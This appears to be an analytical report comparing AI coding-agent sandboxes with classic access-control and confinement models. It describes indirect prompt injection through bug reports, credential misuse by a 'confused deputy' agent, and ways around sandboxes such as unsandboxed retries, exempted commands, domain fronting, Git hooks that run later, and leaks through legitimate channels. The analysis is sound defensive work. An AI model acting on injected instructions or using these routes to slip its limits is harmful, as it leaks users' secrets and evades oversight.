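# Security models for AI agent sandboxes, and how agent sandboxes differ from access control

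## Sandboxes, access control and what counts as a security model

An agent sandbox is a bounded environment in which an AI model runs commands, edits files and calls online services for a user. Access control is the much older practice of deciding which people and programs may do what to which resources. The two overlap because a sandbox has to enforce some access rules, but they do different jobs. A sandbox provides confinement, which means the program inside can affect the outside or send information to it only through checked channels. Authorization means deciding which actions requested through those channels should go ahead. Confinement can work as intended while authorization fails, for instance when an agent emails a confidential file to a stranger from an account it was allowed to use.

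Agent sandboxes are now common, but few come with a security model, meaning a precise account of the adversary, the components that have to work correctly, the states the system can be in, and the property that holds in all of them. The omission is easier to see with some older ideas in hand, most of them from the 1970s and 1980s. (People use the word "sandbox" for several different things. Here it means a mechanism that encloses software in order to impose a security policy on it, and a security policy is the statement of what the software may do.)

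### A coding agent at work

Suppose a developer asks a coding agent to fix a bug. The agent can read the project's repository, run shell commands, and use the developer's credentials, including a token for publishing code and a key to a cloud account. An agent here is an AI model that calls tools in a loop on behalf of a person. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) defines the field in roughly this way. The model only produces text, and a surrounding program, called the harness, turns some of that text into action.

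*Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues, 2026) presents the agent loop as an algorithm. It covers general-purpose assistants, but a coding agent works in much the same way. The harness waits for an event, usually a message from the user. It then gathers the session history, any stored memory and descriptions of the available tools, and uses them to build a system prompt, the standing instructions that the model reads first. The harness sends the model a list containing the system prompt and the user's message, and appends the model's reply to that list. If the reply is a tool call (say, a request to run the test suite), the harness parses it, runs the tool and appends the output too. It then sends the longer list back to the model, and the process repeats until the model signals that the task is complete or the harness reaches its step limit.

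For the bug fix, the tool calls might open the bug report, search the code, change a file, run the tests and publish the result. If the harness runs under the developer's account, the operating system cannot distinguish these actions from the developer's own.

Pirch and colleagues compare this arrangement to an operating system. The model is like an untrusted user, the harness is like the kernel (the privileged core that controls access to hardware and files), and tools are like system calls (the requests that programs make to the kernel). The message list is like working memory. One weakness is that all four agents they tested put trusted and untrusted text into one shared context, whereas operating systems keep each program's memory separate.

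### Prompt injection

Prompt injection exploits that shared context. An attacker places text where an agent will read it, and the agent follows the instructions in it. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) distinguishes direct injection, in which a malicious user types the text into the prompt, from indirect injection, in which the text comes from an outside source such as a web page or email and the user may be an innocent victim. Coding agents constantly read outside material, so indirect injection is the main concern.

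*Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (2025) uses a bug-fixing agent as its running example. The prompt *p* tells the model to inspect a bug report and fix the relevant issues. The harness appends the report *d* to *p*, and the model evaluates the combined string, F(*p*‖*d*). Anyone who can file a bug report can therefore write part of the model's input. If a report includes an instruction to post the cloud key in a public comment, the agent already has the shell and the key it would need to comply.

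*Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) traces this problem from the buffer overflows of the 1990s through SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into a form field and the database runs them. In each case, one channel carries both commands and data, with no structural boundary between them. Programmers can prevent SQL injection by sending the query and the user's input separately, so that a parser keeps them apart. This fix depends on SQL's grammar, but natural language has no grammar that marks some sentences as commands to the reader and others as content, and developers train models to follow instructions wherever they appear.

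Harnesses try to mark the difference between instructions and data with delimiters, role labels and warnings. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) calls these useful engineering practices that "do not create a hard security boundary". A transformer, the kind of network behind today's language models, converts both instructions and data into vectors in a single space. *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) proves that perfect prevention of prompt injection is impossible in such an architecture unless something enforces a separation. The proof does not rule out keeping attackers' success rate low or enforcing the separation outside the model.

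Making the model ignore every instruction it finds would not help either. *Security--Fidelity Tradeoffs* (2026) points out that a model can execute an injected instruction, process it as part of the data, or drop it, and that dropping it looks safe in most benchmarks even when the task needed that text. A bug report, for example, may well contain a command that the developer wants the agent to read. Christodorescu and colleagues go further and argue that an agent's job often includes following instructions it discovers along the way. Tool documentation is meant to change an agent's behaviour, and an agent asked to summarize one issue may reasonably go on to a second issue that the first depends on. On their account, an attack differs from these cases in where the new instruction came from and how much it changes the agent's behaviour, and current agents have trouble establishing even where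 an instruction came from.

The sandbox designer has to assume that the model may be following someone else's instructions at any step. The natural response is to limit what the model can reach.

### The access matrix

The standard way to write down such limits comes from Lampson (1971), in *Protection*. Subjects, the entities that act, label the rows of a table. Objects, the things that need protection, label the columns. Each cell holds the rights that the subject has over the object. (Lampson's own word for the rows was "domains".) For the bug fix, a small matrix might look like this:

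| | Source code | Cloud key | Build log |
|---|---|---|---|
| Developer | owner, read, write | owner, read | read |
| Coding agent | read, write | | read |
| Test runner | read | | write |

An empty cell means no access, so this agent can change the source code but cannot read the cloud key. An agent that runs under the developer's account has no row of its own and gets the developer's permissions, shown in the top row.

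Lampson also gave rules for changing the matrix while the system runs. An object's owner may add rights anywhere in that object's column. A subject may pass on a right it holds only if that right carries a "copy flag". Lampson included the flag because, without it, an undebugged subordinate program could give access away, a concern that applies fairly well to agents.

Most cells in a real matrix are empty, so systems store it as separate columns or rows. Each column is an access-control list. The list for the build log has the developer and the agent as readers and the test runner as a writer, and the system checks it whenever a request for the log comes in. Each row is a set of capabilities, which are unforgeable tokens that each name a resource and grant a right to use it. The coding agent would hold two, one for reading and writing the source code and one for reading the log. This meaning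 of "capabilities" is unrelated to what a model is able to do. Access-control lists make it easy to find out who can access a resource such as the cloud key, while capabilities make it easy to find out which resources a given agent can access.

Access-control schemes also differ in who sets the entries:

- Discretionary control lets the owner of a resource decide who else may use it, as with ordinary file permissions.
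- Mandatory control applies a central policy that owners cannot override.
- Role-based control attaches rights to roles, such as "reviewer", and people get the rights by holding the role.
- Attribute-based control computes each decision from facts about the requester, the resource and the circumstances, such as a file's sensitivity or the time of day.

### The confused deputy

An access matrix can be correct in every cell and still permit a disaster. Hardy (1988), in *The Confused Deputy*, describes an example from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers, in a story he calls nearly true. The compiler recorded usage statistics in a file in its directory, SYSX, so the operators gave it permission to write files there. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output, and one user named the billing file, which was also in SYSX. Because the compiler had permission to write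 in that directory, the operating system let it open the file, and the debugging output overwrote the billing records.

Hardy could not find a faulty line of code. The code for writing debugging output was correct when it was written and became wrong only when the compiler got its new permission. He concluded that the compiler ran with authority from two sources, the user and its own licence, and had no way to specify which one to use. A confused deputy is a program that someone leads into using its legitimate authority for them when they lack that authority themselves. Tymshare first added a system call for switching between the two authorities, but soon found applications that needed more than two. Hardy preferred capabilities. The user would give the compiler a token for the output file instead of the file's name, and a user without a token for the billing file could not give it one.

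A coding agent with a developer's credentials and a stranger's bug report in its context is in the same position as Hardy's compiler, but Hardy's remedy only partly applies. The compiler used each authority at known places in its code, so a programmer could tie the right token to each place. In an agent, the model picks which token to use after reading the stranger's text, so the text can influence the choice.

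### The reference monitor

Access rules protect little unless something enforces them every time. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), a report for the US Air Force, described a reference monitor, which checks every reference to a program, file or device against a list of what the subject, such as a user, may do. The Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one machine, and Anderson's panel assumed that some legitimate users would be malicious and could write their own programs. The report set three requirements for the monitor: nobody can tamper with it, every access goes through it, and it is small enough to analyse and test completely.

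The panel then applied them to a Honeywell operating system, GCOS III. The hardware kept each user's program inside its own area of memory, but the operating system suspended that check when it performed input and output on the program's behalf, so some accesses bypassed the monitor. GCOS itself could not qualify as the monitor either, because its 200,000 or 300,000 instructions were far too many to analyse.

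The same test is hard for agent safeguards to pass. A line in the system prompt telling the model never to read the cloud key fails because an attacker's text enters the same context. Pirch and colleagues describe such guidance as suggestion rather than enforcement. A check in the harness on each call to the file-reading tool works better, but the agent can bypass it by opening the same file through the shell. The trusted computing base, or trusted base, is the set of components that must work correctly for a security property to hold. Much of sandbox design involves keeping this base small and keeping the model out of it.

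### The confinement problem

Even when every read and write is checked, a program may still leak data it is allowed to read. In *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, Lampson (1973) imagined a customer who gives private data to a service, which is a program that somebody else wrote. The service needs the data to do its work, and the problem is how the customer can stop it from passing the data to the service's owner.

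Lampson listed ways a service could leak data. The service might write to a file that its owner can read, send the owner a message, or encode the data in the bill. If the system prevents one program from writing to a file while another is reading it, the service can send bits by opening and closing a file it has permission only to read, and another program can receive them by checking when the file is locked. The service can also vary how much it computes, which a program running at the same time can detect as changes in the machine's speed. Lampson sorted these methods into storage, legitimate channels such as the bill, and covert channels, which were not intended to carry information at all.

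Total isolation would prevent every leak, but Lampson rejected it as impractical because it would forbid even routine requests to the operating system, which can leak information. He proposed that any program a confined program calls must be either trusted or confined too, and that the customer should determine everything that goes into the remaining channels. Where that is too burdensome, one can instead limit how many bits per second leak out. He doubted that any rigorous method would find every channel in even a moderately complex system.

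A coding agent can leak a secret key through many legitimate channels, such as commit messages, comments on bug reports and the names of packages it requests from a public registry. Lampson also assumed that a confined program keeps no memory between calls, since it could otherwise store data and leak it later. Many agents break this assumption because they are designed to keep long-term memory.

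### Containers, gVisor and microVMs

An agent sandbox is usually built on one of three mechanisms that cloud companies use to keep customers' programs apart. The mechanisms differ mainly in which kernel the sandboxed program can make system calls to.

A container is a group of ordinary processes that run on the host machine's own kernel with restrictions around them. *Firecracker* (Agache, Brooker and colleagues, 2020) describes how Linux imposes these restrictions. Namespaces give the processes their own view of user accounts, process numbers and network interfaces, control groups cap their use of processor and memory, and a filter limits which system calls they can make. The paper treats the filter as the most important security boundary of these. A stricter filter is safer but compatible with fewer programs. A trivial Linux program needs 15 different system calls, while a typical installation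 of Ubuntu 15.04 needs 224. An agent that installs packages and runs whatever build tools a project uses will need a permissive filter, and any flaw in the kernel code behind the permitted calls could let the agent escape the container. Google Cloud wrote that "Traditional Linux containers are not sandboxes" when it introduced gVisor as an alternative.

gVisor puts a second kernel in between. According to the gVisor project's *Introduction to gVisor security*, a component with the name Sentry intercepts the program's system calls and handles them itself, using a reimplementation of Linux in the programming language Go. When a program asks for its process number, the Sentry answers from its own table and the host kernel never hears of it. The Sentry does make some calls to the host, but from a much shorter list, and it never passes the program's calls straight through. To break out, an attacker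 would have to exploit both the Sentry and the host kernel, which share no code. The price is that a program cannot use any kernel feature that the Sentry lacks.

A microVM is a lightweight virtual machine that gives the program its own complete Linux kernel. The designers treat that kernel as hostile and confine it with the processor's virtualization hardware and a small program on the host, the virtual machine monitor. Virtual machines used to take seconds to start. Agache and colleagues, who built the Firecracker monitor at Amazon, report that a microVM starts running application code in under 125 milliseconds and has less than 5 megabytes of memory overhead. Firecracker has about 50,000 lines of code, while QEMU, the usual monitor, has more than 1.4 million. The trusted base also includes Linux on the host, which Firecracker depends on for scheduling, memory and storage.

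A microVM or gVisor is harder to escape than a container, but none of the three controls what a program does with whatever is inside the sandbox. The gVisor project lists among its limits that an attacker who takes over the program still has whatever access the sandbox's configuration gives it. If the developer puts a cloud key and a network connection inside a microVM, the agent can send the key out without attacking anything.

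### What makes something a security model

Anderson blamed much of the insecurity of computer systems in 1972 on "the absence of models". Without a model, designers added protections piecemeal and could not tell whether they had covered everything. Hiring experts to break in could not show this either, because other attackers might succeed where those experts failed.

*Secure Computer Systems* (Bell and LaPadula, 1973) gives the best-known model, which is for protecting military secrets. A state of the system is a triple (*b*, *M*, *f*). The set *b* contains the subject–object pairs in which the subject currently has access to the object, *M* is the access matrix, and *f* assigns a clearance to each subject, a classification to each object, and need-to-know categories to both. A state is secure if, for every pair (*S*, *O*) in *b*, the clearance of *S* is at least as high as the classification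 of *O*, and *S* has every need-to-know category that *O* has. A relation *W* lists the moves the system can make in response to requests.

They prove that if every move in *W* leaves *f* unchanged and adds to *b* only pairs that meet the condition just given, then a system that starts in a secure state stays secure. The proof is by induction. If a state is secure, its existing pairs remain acceptable after a move because their labels have not changed, and any new pairs are acceptable by assumption, so the next state is also secure.

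If the cloud key has a high classification and the agent has a low clearance, the theorem shows that no sequence of requests can give the agent access to the key. This covers attacks that nobody has thought of, which testing cannot do. The theorem also rests on assumptions that anyone can inspect. Bell and LaPadula warned that it does not apply unless the real system guarantees that *W* is inviolable. Rushby (1986), in *The Bell and La Padula Security Model*, found that they had also assumed, without stating it, that the machine actually restricts each subject to the accesses on record. A reference monitor has to make both assumptions true.

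A proof is only as good as its definition of security, and this one needed repair. In the 1973 version, a program with high clearance could read a secret and copy it into an unclassified file. Bell and LaPadula later added the \*-property (pronounced "star-property"), which Rushby restates in modern notation. An untrusted subject may read only objects at or below its current level and may alter only objects at or above it. It follows that if the subject can read one object and alter another, the altered object has a classification at least as high as the one it reads, so secrets cannot drift downward. (Noninterference and label lattices generalize the idea.)

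Bell and LaPadula had written down exactly what they meant by "secure", so McLean (1987), in *Reasoning About Security Models*, could challenge their definition with a counterexample. His System Z responds to any request for access by downgrading every subject and object to the lowest level and then granting the request. Every state it reaches meets the definition of secure, yet everyone can read everything. McLean concluded that no definition that covers only states can be adequate, and that a model must also restrict the transitions between them. The original theorem, with its fixed labels, would have excluded System Z, but in the same 1973 report Bell and LaPadula also proved a version in which classifications may fall while the system runs. Bell (1988), in *Concerning “Modeling” of Computer Security*, answered that a model is an abstraction for studying a problem, as in physics or engineering,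 and that McLean had confused this with a different, foundational notion of a model. He may be right, but an engineer who relies on the theorem still has to ask who may change the labels.

Bell and LaPadula wrote that a model of a secure computer must have "absolute rather than probabilistic determinacy", a demand that is especially hard for agents to meet. A language model can give different answers to the same prompt, and training it never to do something only makes the behaviour unlikely, with a probability that depends on what else is in the context. Christodorescu and colleagues consider a reference monitor that correctly refuses 99% of unauthorized requests, but an attacker can search for the 1% it allows.

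## What today's agent sandboxes promise and what they leave unstated

Researchers were already vague about sandboxes before AI agents. *A systematic analysis of the science of sandboxing* (Maass and colleagues, 2016) reviews ten years of papers from five leading conferences on security and operating systems, and identifies 101 that might describe a sandbox. Of these, 49 used the word "sandbox" at least once, and 14 defined it clearly enough for the reviewers to characterize the definition.

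Seven of the definitions treated a sandbox as encapsulation, a bounded place where a faulty or hostile program cannot harm anything else, and the other seven treated it as the enforcement of a policy about what the program may do. One technique, software-based fault isolation, appeared in both groups. It rewrites a program's instructions so that the program cannot touch memory outside its own region. Maass and colleagues concluded that the two groups of definitions covered different aspects of the same thing. This report uses their definition, which combines the enclosure with the policy, so a full description of a sandbox must include its policy.

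The reviewers also found that researchers rarely proved their security claims. In 29 papers, the researchers ran one kind of empirical test and used ad hoc arguments for what it didn't cover. These arguments often amounted to "Our sandbox is secure because the design is secure". Of the 42 papers that tested security empirically, 22 used non-public data, so nobody could compare their results with those of other sandboxes. Performance testing improved over the decade (the rank correlation with publication year was 0.30), but security testing did not (−0.02).

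In 48 of the sandboxes in the review, the designers had built in a fixed policy, which usually protected a program's memory or code. Another 17 required users to write the policy themselves, and these covered a wider range of resources, including files and communications. Six papers proved that a mechanism correctly enforced a fixed policy, but none tried to prove that a mechanism could enforce every policy a user might write. A fixed rule such as "never jump to code outside this region" suits almost any program, but a coding agent's sandbox mostly governs files and network connections, where the right limits depend on the project and the task.

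### Five current sandboxes

Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, has a sandbox that is on by default. According to OpenAI's *Sandbox*, it covers the commands that Codex launches, such as Git or a test runner, as well as Codex's own file operations. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* lists the default limits for local work. Commands have no network access and can write only to the workspace (the current project and some temporary directories). Reading is much less restricted. In OpenAI's account of the Windows version, Codex can by default "read files almost anywhere". The agent can therefore read a cloud key in the developer's home directory, but its shell commands can't send the key over the network. The key could still leave the machine, because the model runs in the cloud and whatever the agent reads goes to OpenAI. The agent might also copy the key into a source file that the developer later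 publishes.

When a task needs more access, Codex asks for approval, and users can write rules that let particular commands run outside the sandbox. OpenAI presents the benefit as a clearer "trust model", in which the user relies on enforced limits and not just on the agent's intentions. This amounts to a promise that the limits will hold, but not that they are the right limits for protecting a particular secret.

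Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has a sandbox that is off by default and covers only shell commands. According to Anthropic's documentation, when the sandbox is on, commands can write to the working directory and a temporary directory, and Claude Code normally asks before a command contacts a new domain. The tools that read files, edit them and fetch web pages run outside the sandbox and follow permission rules instead. If the user sets the sandbox to block shell commands from reading a file, Claude's file-reading tool can still open it. Hooks (scripts that run automatically at set points) and local servers that provide extra tools run with the user's full access.

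There are two more ways around this sandbox. When a command fails inside it, Claude may retry the command outside, and the user's settings determine who, if anyone, must approve the retry. If the sandbox cannot start, Claude Code runs commands without it unless a setting forbids this. Administrators can disable both behaviors. Even then, the shell sandbox would fail Anderson's test for a reference monitor of the whole agent, because many of the agent's accesses never pass through it. Anthropic's *Choose a sandbox environment* advises users who want to leave Claude unattended to put the entire process inside a container, a virtual machine or a wrapper called the sandbox runtime.

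Anthropic has also described this sandbox's protection differently in its announcement and its documentation. When it introduced the feature, Anthropic wrote that network isolation prevents a prompt-injected Claude from leaking sensitive information. In the documentation, it warns that allowing a broad domain such as github.com can create paths for leaking data. The proxy that filters connections also relies on the host name the program gives it and does not inspect encrypted traffic by default, so a program may be able to name an allowed host and reach a different one, a trick known as domain fronting. The sandbox roughly guarantees that shell commands connect only to allowed hosts unless they disguise the destination, which is a narrower guarantee than preventing leaks.

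Users of Gemini CLI, Google's command-line agent, enable its sandbox with a flag, an environment variable or a setting. Google's *Sandboxing in Gemini CLI* lists benefits that include limiting file access to the project directory, preventing accidental damage and reducing risk from untrusted code. The default macOS profile confines writes to the project directory but allows broad file reads and network access, so an agent hijacked by prompt injection could read a key and send it anywhere. That profile helps much more with accidental damage to files than with theft. Google also offers stricter profiles, including some that restrict reads or route traffic through a proxy.

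NVIDIA makes the most ambitious promise of the group for OpenShell, its general-purpose environment for running agents. It writes that OpenShell's layers of protection "prevent unauthorized data access, credential exposure, and network exfiltration". According to NVIDIA's *Which agent sandbox enforces default-deny networking* (2026), every outgoing TCP connection passes through a proxy and needs a matching policy rule. The default file policy leaves out the places where the host stores credentials, and NVIDIA notes that the file policy cannot change while the sandbox is running. A supervisor inside each sandbox starts the agent as a restricted process and enforces the policy, so it belongs to the trusted base even though it shares the sandbox with the agent.

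What counts as "unauthorized" in NVIDIA's promise depends on the policy. If the policy allows connections to a public code host, a rule about destinations cannot distinguish sending a bug fix there from sending a stolen key. NVIDIA's *OpenShell Security Best Practices for Controls, Risks, and Configuration Guidance* does go beyond listing mechanisms by explaining what each control protects and what a user risks by relaxing it.

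*SideKernel* (Prasakis, 2026), a student project, has one of the clearest threat models. It presents a microVM sandbox for running coding agents on a Mac and treats the agent as the adversary, whether an injected instruction or the model's own error made it hostile. The agent has full privileges inside the sandbox. At the "south boundary" with the host, the sandbox is meant to protect the host's running system and any files the user has not shared. At the "north boundary" with the internet and other machines, it is meant to stop the agent from leaking data or attacking outsiders.

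Prasakis also lists the risks that the design accepts. For example, the agent can destroy anything in the shared project folder and expose a malicious service on the host's ports. A switch blocks all outgoing traffic except to Claude's API, which the agent needs to work. This protection against leaks is incomplete because the API connection is a legitimate channel of the kind Lampson described, and the design does not limit what may pass through it.

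| Sandbox | On by default? | Default limits | What is outside | Promise, and whom it protects | What the promise leaves unstated |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Codex (local) | Yes | Writes only to the workspace; no network for commands; broad reads | Approved exceptions | The user can rely on enforced limits | Whether secrets may reach files that the developer later publishes |
| Claude Code (shell sandbox) | No | Writes to the working and temporary directories; approval for new domains | File and web tools, hooks, local tool servers, some retries | The user is safe from leaks and system changes by an injected agent | Whether sending data to an approved domain counts as a leak |
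| Gemini CLI (macOS profile) | No | Writes only to the project; broad reads and network | Depends on the chosen method | The user is safer from accidents and untrusted code | Whether files outside the project should stay secret |
| OpenShell | Yes, for agents run in it | Network connections need a rule; no access to host credential paths | The gateway that manages sandboxes | The operator is safe from unauthorized access and leaks | What counts as unauthorized beyond breaking the configured policy |
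| SideKernel | Yes, for agents run in it | Project folder shared; other host files need approval | The virtual machine monitor and credential proxy | The host, its data and outsiders are safe from a hostile agent | How much data may leave through Claude's API |

### Files that run later

Some of the most detailed rules in these products concern dangers that remain after the agent has finished. The makers of Zed, a code editor, warn that an agent inside a sandbox can write Git settings that make Git run a program later, when the developer uses a terminal outside the sandbox. Some terminals run Git every time they display a prompt, so the developer may not have to type a command.

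OpenAI makes the `.git` directory read-only in Codex's default sandbox. Anthropic's sandbox runtime blocks writes to shell startup files and to Git's hooks, which are scripts that Git runs automatically. Anthropic explains that on macOS the runtime checks these rules at each write. On Linux it builds the list of blocked paths when it starts, so the list does not cover repositories that the agent creates or downloads during the session.

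These lists of protected files suggest a more general property, roughly that nothing the agent writes will later run with the developer's full authority. No coding sandbox could promise exactly that, because the agent's job is to write code that somebody will run. The property needs an exception for code the developer has reviewed, and a definition of adequate review. Without a stated property, it is hard to tell whether a path missing from the list is a bug or a risk the designers accepted. An exemption can also easily undo this protection. In Anthropic's example, if a user exempts `docker compose` from the shell sandbox, Claude can write the file that the command reads and then run the command with the user's full access.

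### Eleven harnesses and 39 papers

*Harness Engineering* (Barbaste, Darrigol and colleagues, 2026) compared how much eleven coding harnesses invest in isolation, based on their source code as of July 2026. It rated the investment as substantial in Codex and OpenHands, moderate in Claude Code and Gemini CLI, and light in Mini-SWE-Agent, a minimal research harness. Hermes leaves isolation to the environment the user runs it in. The other five (Mistral Vibe, Pi, OpenCode, Aider and OpenClaw) have no built-in sandbox.

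Codebase size does not explain the difference. Hermes has about 642,000 lines of code and OpenCode about 578,000, yet neither includes its own operating-system-level isolation. Their developers focused on other controls. When Hermes runs directly on the user's machine, it blocks a short list of catastrophic commands, such as erasing a disk, even if the user has turned off approvals. OpenCode parses each shell command and applies permission rules to it. Barbaste and colleagues point out that "sandbox" in OpenCode's code means a Git worktree, which is a separate working copy of a repository. A worktree keeps two lines of development from colliding but does not restrict what a program can reach.

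Pi's developers deliberately left out a sandbox, so its tools run with all of the user's permissions unless the user adds an extension or outside isolation. The developers argue that a partial sandbox inside the harness "would be easy to misunderstand as a security boundary". This is a fair criticism of products whose defaults cover only some tools, but Pi users who add nothing are less protected than users of a partial sandbox.

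Research on isolation and access control is also split. In *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents*, Rashidi (2026) sorted 39 papers on the boundary between agents and the machines they act on into 17 categories. Of these papers, 31 are from 2025 and 2026. Five propose or evaluate isolation and six propose access controls, but none of these eleven compares an isolation mechanism with an access control mechanism on a shared benchmark. Readers therefore can't tell whether a tighter container or a better permission system would stop more of the same attacks, or how much combining them would help.

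Rashidi identifies four other gaps:

- Researchers have measured how often real lists of forbidden commands fail, but the people who design defences do not test them against those failures.
- One group studies agents that check a file or web page and then act after it has changed, while another studies tools whose descriptions become malicious after approval. Both problems come from trusting an old check, but the two groups do not cite each other.
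- Every enforcement mechanism in the collection assumes that a trustworthy author has written the policy correctly.
- No access-control paper addresses agents that take harmless-looking extra steps, which the user never requested but the permissions allow.

The evidence that the research is fragmented is good but indirect. Rashidi infers the gaps from missing citations and comparisons, and acknowledges that the search was not exhaustive. Eight of the 17 categories contain only one paper, which could mean that the topic is new or that the search missed other papers. The lack of head-to-head tests matters more than the exact number of categories, because it leaves sandbox designers with little evidence about which property their mechanism is best suited to provide.

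### Where testable properties can be found

Official and industry texts give designers part of what they need to define a testable property. Rashidi notes that OWASP, a nonprofit that publishes guidance on software security, lists "excessive agency" among the top ten risks for applications built on language models. Naming the risk helps designers notice it, but to test a sandbox they would also need to know which actions are excessive for a given agent and task.

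Vulnerability reports can be more precise. Rashidi checked four against the database run by NIST, the US standards institute, and two of them concern Claude Code's prompt asking whether the user trusts a project. In one, older versions could run code from the project before the user accepted. In the other, a malicious repository could extract data, including API keys, before the user confirmed. Anthropic has fixed both. Together they imply a rule that nothing in the repository may run or cause data to leave until the user agrees. A tester could check that rule, but it covers only the start of a session. It sets no limits on what can happen if a project the user has accepted later turns out to contain a malicious bug report.

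The hacking contest Pwn2Own Berlin 2026 had a category for coding agents, with Claude Code, Codex and Cursor as the targets. Contestants demonstrated vulnerabilities in all three. Rashidi reports that an entry had to exploit a vulnerability through ordinary use of the agent and material the contestant controlled, such as a web page or repository. The organizers excluded jailbreaks that did not "cross security boundaries" and attacks that depended on unsafe modes. These rules are useful because they separate odd model output from a breach, but they work only if someone has already decided where each product's boundary lies.

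Codex lets users attach examples to a command rule, showing which commands it should and should not match. Barbaste and colleagues found that Codex checks these examples whenever it loads the rules. For instance, someone who writes a rule to allow `git status` can confirm that it does not also allow `git push`. These checks test whether a rule matches the commands its author intended, but not whether the allowed commands could combine to leak a key.

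### Why the statement is missing

The gap comes partly from the inherited word "sandbox". OpenAI defines a sandbox as "a constrained execution environment", which fits every product in the table and so doesn't distinguish between them. In OpenCode the term has no security meaning. But a shared definition would probably not change much by itself. Maass and colleagues published a good one in 2016, but a designer who adopts it still has to choose a policy.

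Comparing products by their isolation mechanism seems to be more harmful. Prasakis lists 22 sandboxes and records whether each is open source, runs locally, provides a shell, uses a microVM and works on a Mac. The list also gives each sandbox's isolation mechanism, such as a container or Apple's Seatbelt, but not the adversary it is meant to stop or the security property it is meant to protect. This suits Prasakis's purpose of finding products similar to SideKernel. The 23 tests that follow concern convenience and features, such as whether the user can paste an image or block network traffic. SideKernel and Docker Sandboxes, Docker's microVM product, each passed 19. A pass means only that the feature exists, so the scores do not measure how well either product resists attack.

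Containers and Seatbelt both share the host's kernel but restrict programs differently, so Prasakis asks which threat model to use when comparing Seatbelt with a microVM, and leaves the answer to a separate study. Marketing is often less careful about threat models. NVIDIA's *Which self-hosted agent sandbox gives stronger security guarantees than cloud-based alternatives?* (2026) supports its answer by listing mechanisms, including Landlock, the part of the Linux kernel that restricts file access. NVIDIA argues that Landlock's restrictions hold even when container boundaries are insufficient. That is plausible if the container is misconfigured, but an attacker who takes over the shared kernel can also switch off Landlock. Readers who agree about every mechanism on NVIDIA's list could still disagree about whether the guarantee is stronger if they have different attackers in mind.

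Local and hosted sandboxes also protect different people. On a laptop, the main concern is the developer's own machine and credentials. A company that runs agents for many customers has to protect its servers and isolate customers from one another. OpenAI's *Sandbox security* advises developers of such services to use separate environments for users or workloads that must not share data. That separation alone would not stop an agent from leaking its own user's key.

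Some hosted products also keep the user's original secrets from the agent. In the cloud version of Codex, user-configured secrets are available during environment setup, and OpenAI removes them before the agent starts. In its cloud sessions, Anthropic keeps the user's GitHub token outside the sandbox and supplies a more limited credential inside. These measures support the useful claim that the agent never holds the original secret. A provider could state and test this claim separately from the claim that customers cannot reach each other.

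Such claims are harder to assemble because one group of researchers works on isolation and another on permissions. This division is probably a secondary reason the claims are missing, since companies write their own documentation and could state a security property even if the two groups never cited each other. A single student did so for SideKernel.

The most persistent cause of these gaps is that nobody has settled who should write the policy. OpenAI knows how Codex enforces a rule against writing outside the workspace, but only the developer or the developer's employer knows which files are confidential and which recipients are legitimate. Companies therefore supply defaults and leave the harder decisions to the user. Anthropic makes users responsible for allowing only trusted domains. OpenAI advises users in its security documentation to add controls at a lower layer if hostile DNS (an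 attacker manipulating the internet's address lookups) is "in scope". Users thus have to choose part of the threat model, often without knowing they have a choice.

Several parties can contribute to a policy. The vendor sets the defaults, an administrator may lock some settings, the developer adds exceptions, and the project can include its own settings file. Claude Code merges settings from many of these sources. According to Anthropic, in versions before 2.1.285, a project's settings could re-enable retrying commands outside the sandbox after a user had turned that option off in their own settings. Because a stranger may have written the project, a potential attacker could set part of the policy. In one of Claude Code's modes, the model lists the hosts a command needs and a second model reviews the request, so the agent helps set its own limits.

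Organizations can reduce confusion about who is responsible for an agent's sandbox policy by setting it themselves. OpenAI requires its staff to run Codex in a sandbox, and its policy allows expected network destinations, blocks some others and requires approval for unfamiliar ones. Because of these approvals, some decisions are still made while the agent is working. A developer who uses an agent alone has no administrator to make the other decisions.

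### Useful engineering without a formal model

Arguably, none of this should delay a useful product. Codex blocks network access by default, which makes stealing a key harder even if nobody has defined exfiltration. The bigger problem may be that many people don't use a sandbox at all. In an informal survey by Prasakis, 26 of 68 coding-agent users currently ran their agents in a sandbox, and 35 had never done so. Prasakis recruited respondents through a professional network, a startup community and a university, so the percentages may not apply to other users. Most of those 35 had not even considered using a sandbox, and a formal security proof would probably not change that.

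The 2016 review offers some support for putting engineering first. Maass and colleagues found only four cases in which industry had clearly adopted a sandbox from their collection or its technique. Three of the four came from industry or from people with close ties to it. Google designed Native Client for Chrome, for instance, and the creator of systrace, which filters a program's system calls, published working code with the paper. Four cases are too few to establish a rule, but researchers had improved some of the other techniques for decades with almost no adoption. Maass and colleagues suspected this was largely because the techniques were hard to use.

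The same review shows the harm in leaving the policy vague. Developers made mistakes when applying sandboxes to Chrome, Adobe Reader and Java programs, and attackers widely exploited the resulting holes. In each case the developers had to do much of the work by hand and could not easily be sure they had imposed the policy they wanted. Even with a better-built sandbox, they would still have had to work out what that policy was.

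A company can improve on this without a complete formal model. Maass and colleagues recommend assurance cases, which engineers developed after fatal accidents in physical systems. An assurance case breaks a broad claim into smaller ones and attaches evidence to each. For the shell sandbox in Claude Code, "an injected agent cannot leak secrets" would break into separate claims about shell commands, file tools, approved domains and retries outside the sandbox. Anthropic already documents exceptions in each of these areas, so it would have to narrow the broad claim to account for them.

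## The view that stronger isolation is enough

A missing policy matters less if the sandbox is hard to escape and holds little of value. A hijacked agent can then do little damage, and nobody has to work out every rule in advance.

On this view, an agent is untrusted code, and cloud companies have run strangers' code for years. Isolation works the same way whatever the model intends. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* (May 2026) groups the risks into careless or malicious users, models that take harmful actions nobody requested, and outside attackers. A network block can stop a stolen key from leaving in all three cases, while safeguards in the model only lower the odds of a leak. On one prompt injection benchmark, attackers succeeded against Claude Opus 4.7 about 0.1% of the time with a single attempt, but 5–6% with 100 adaptive attempts.

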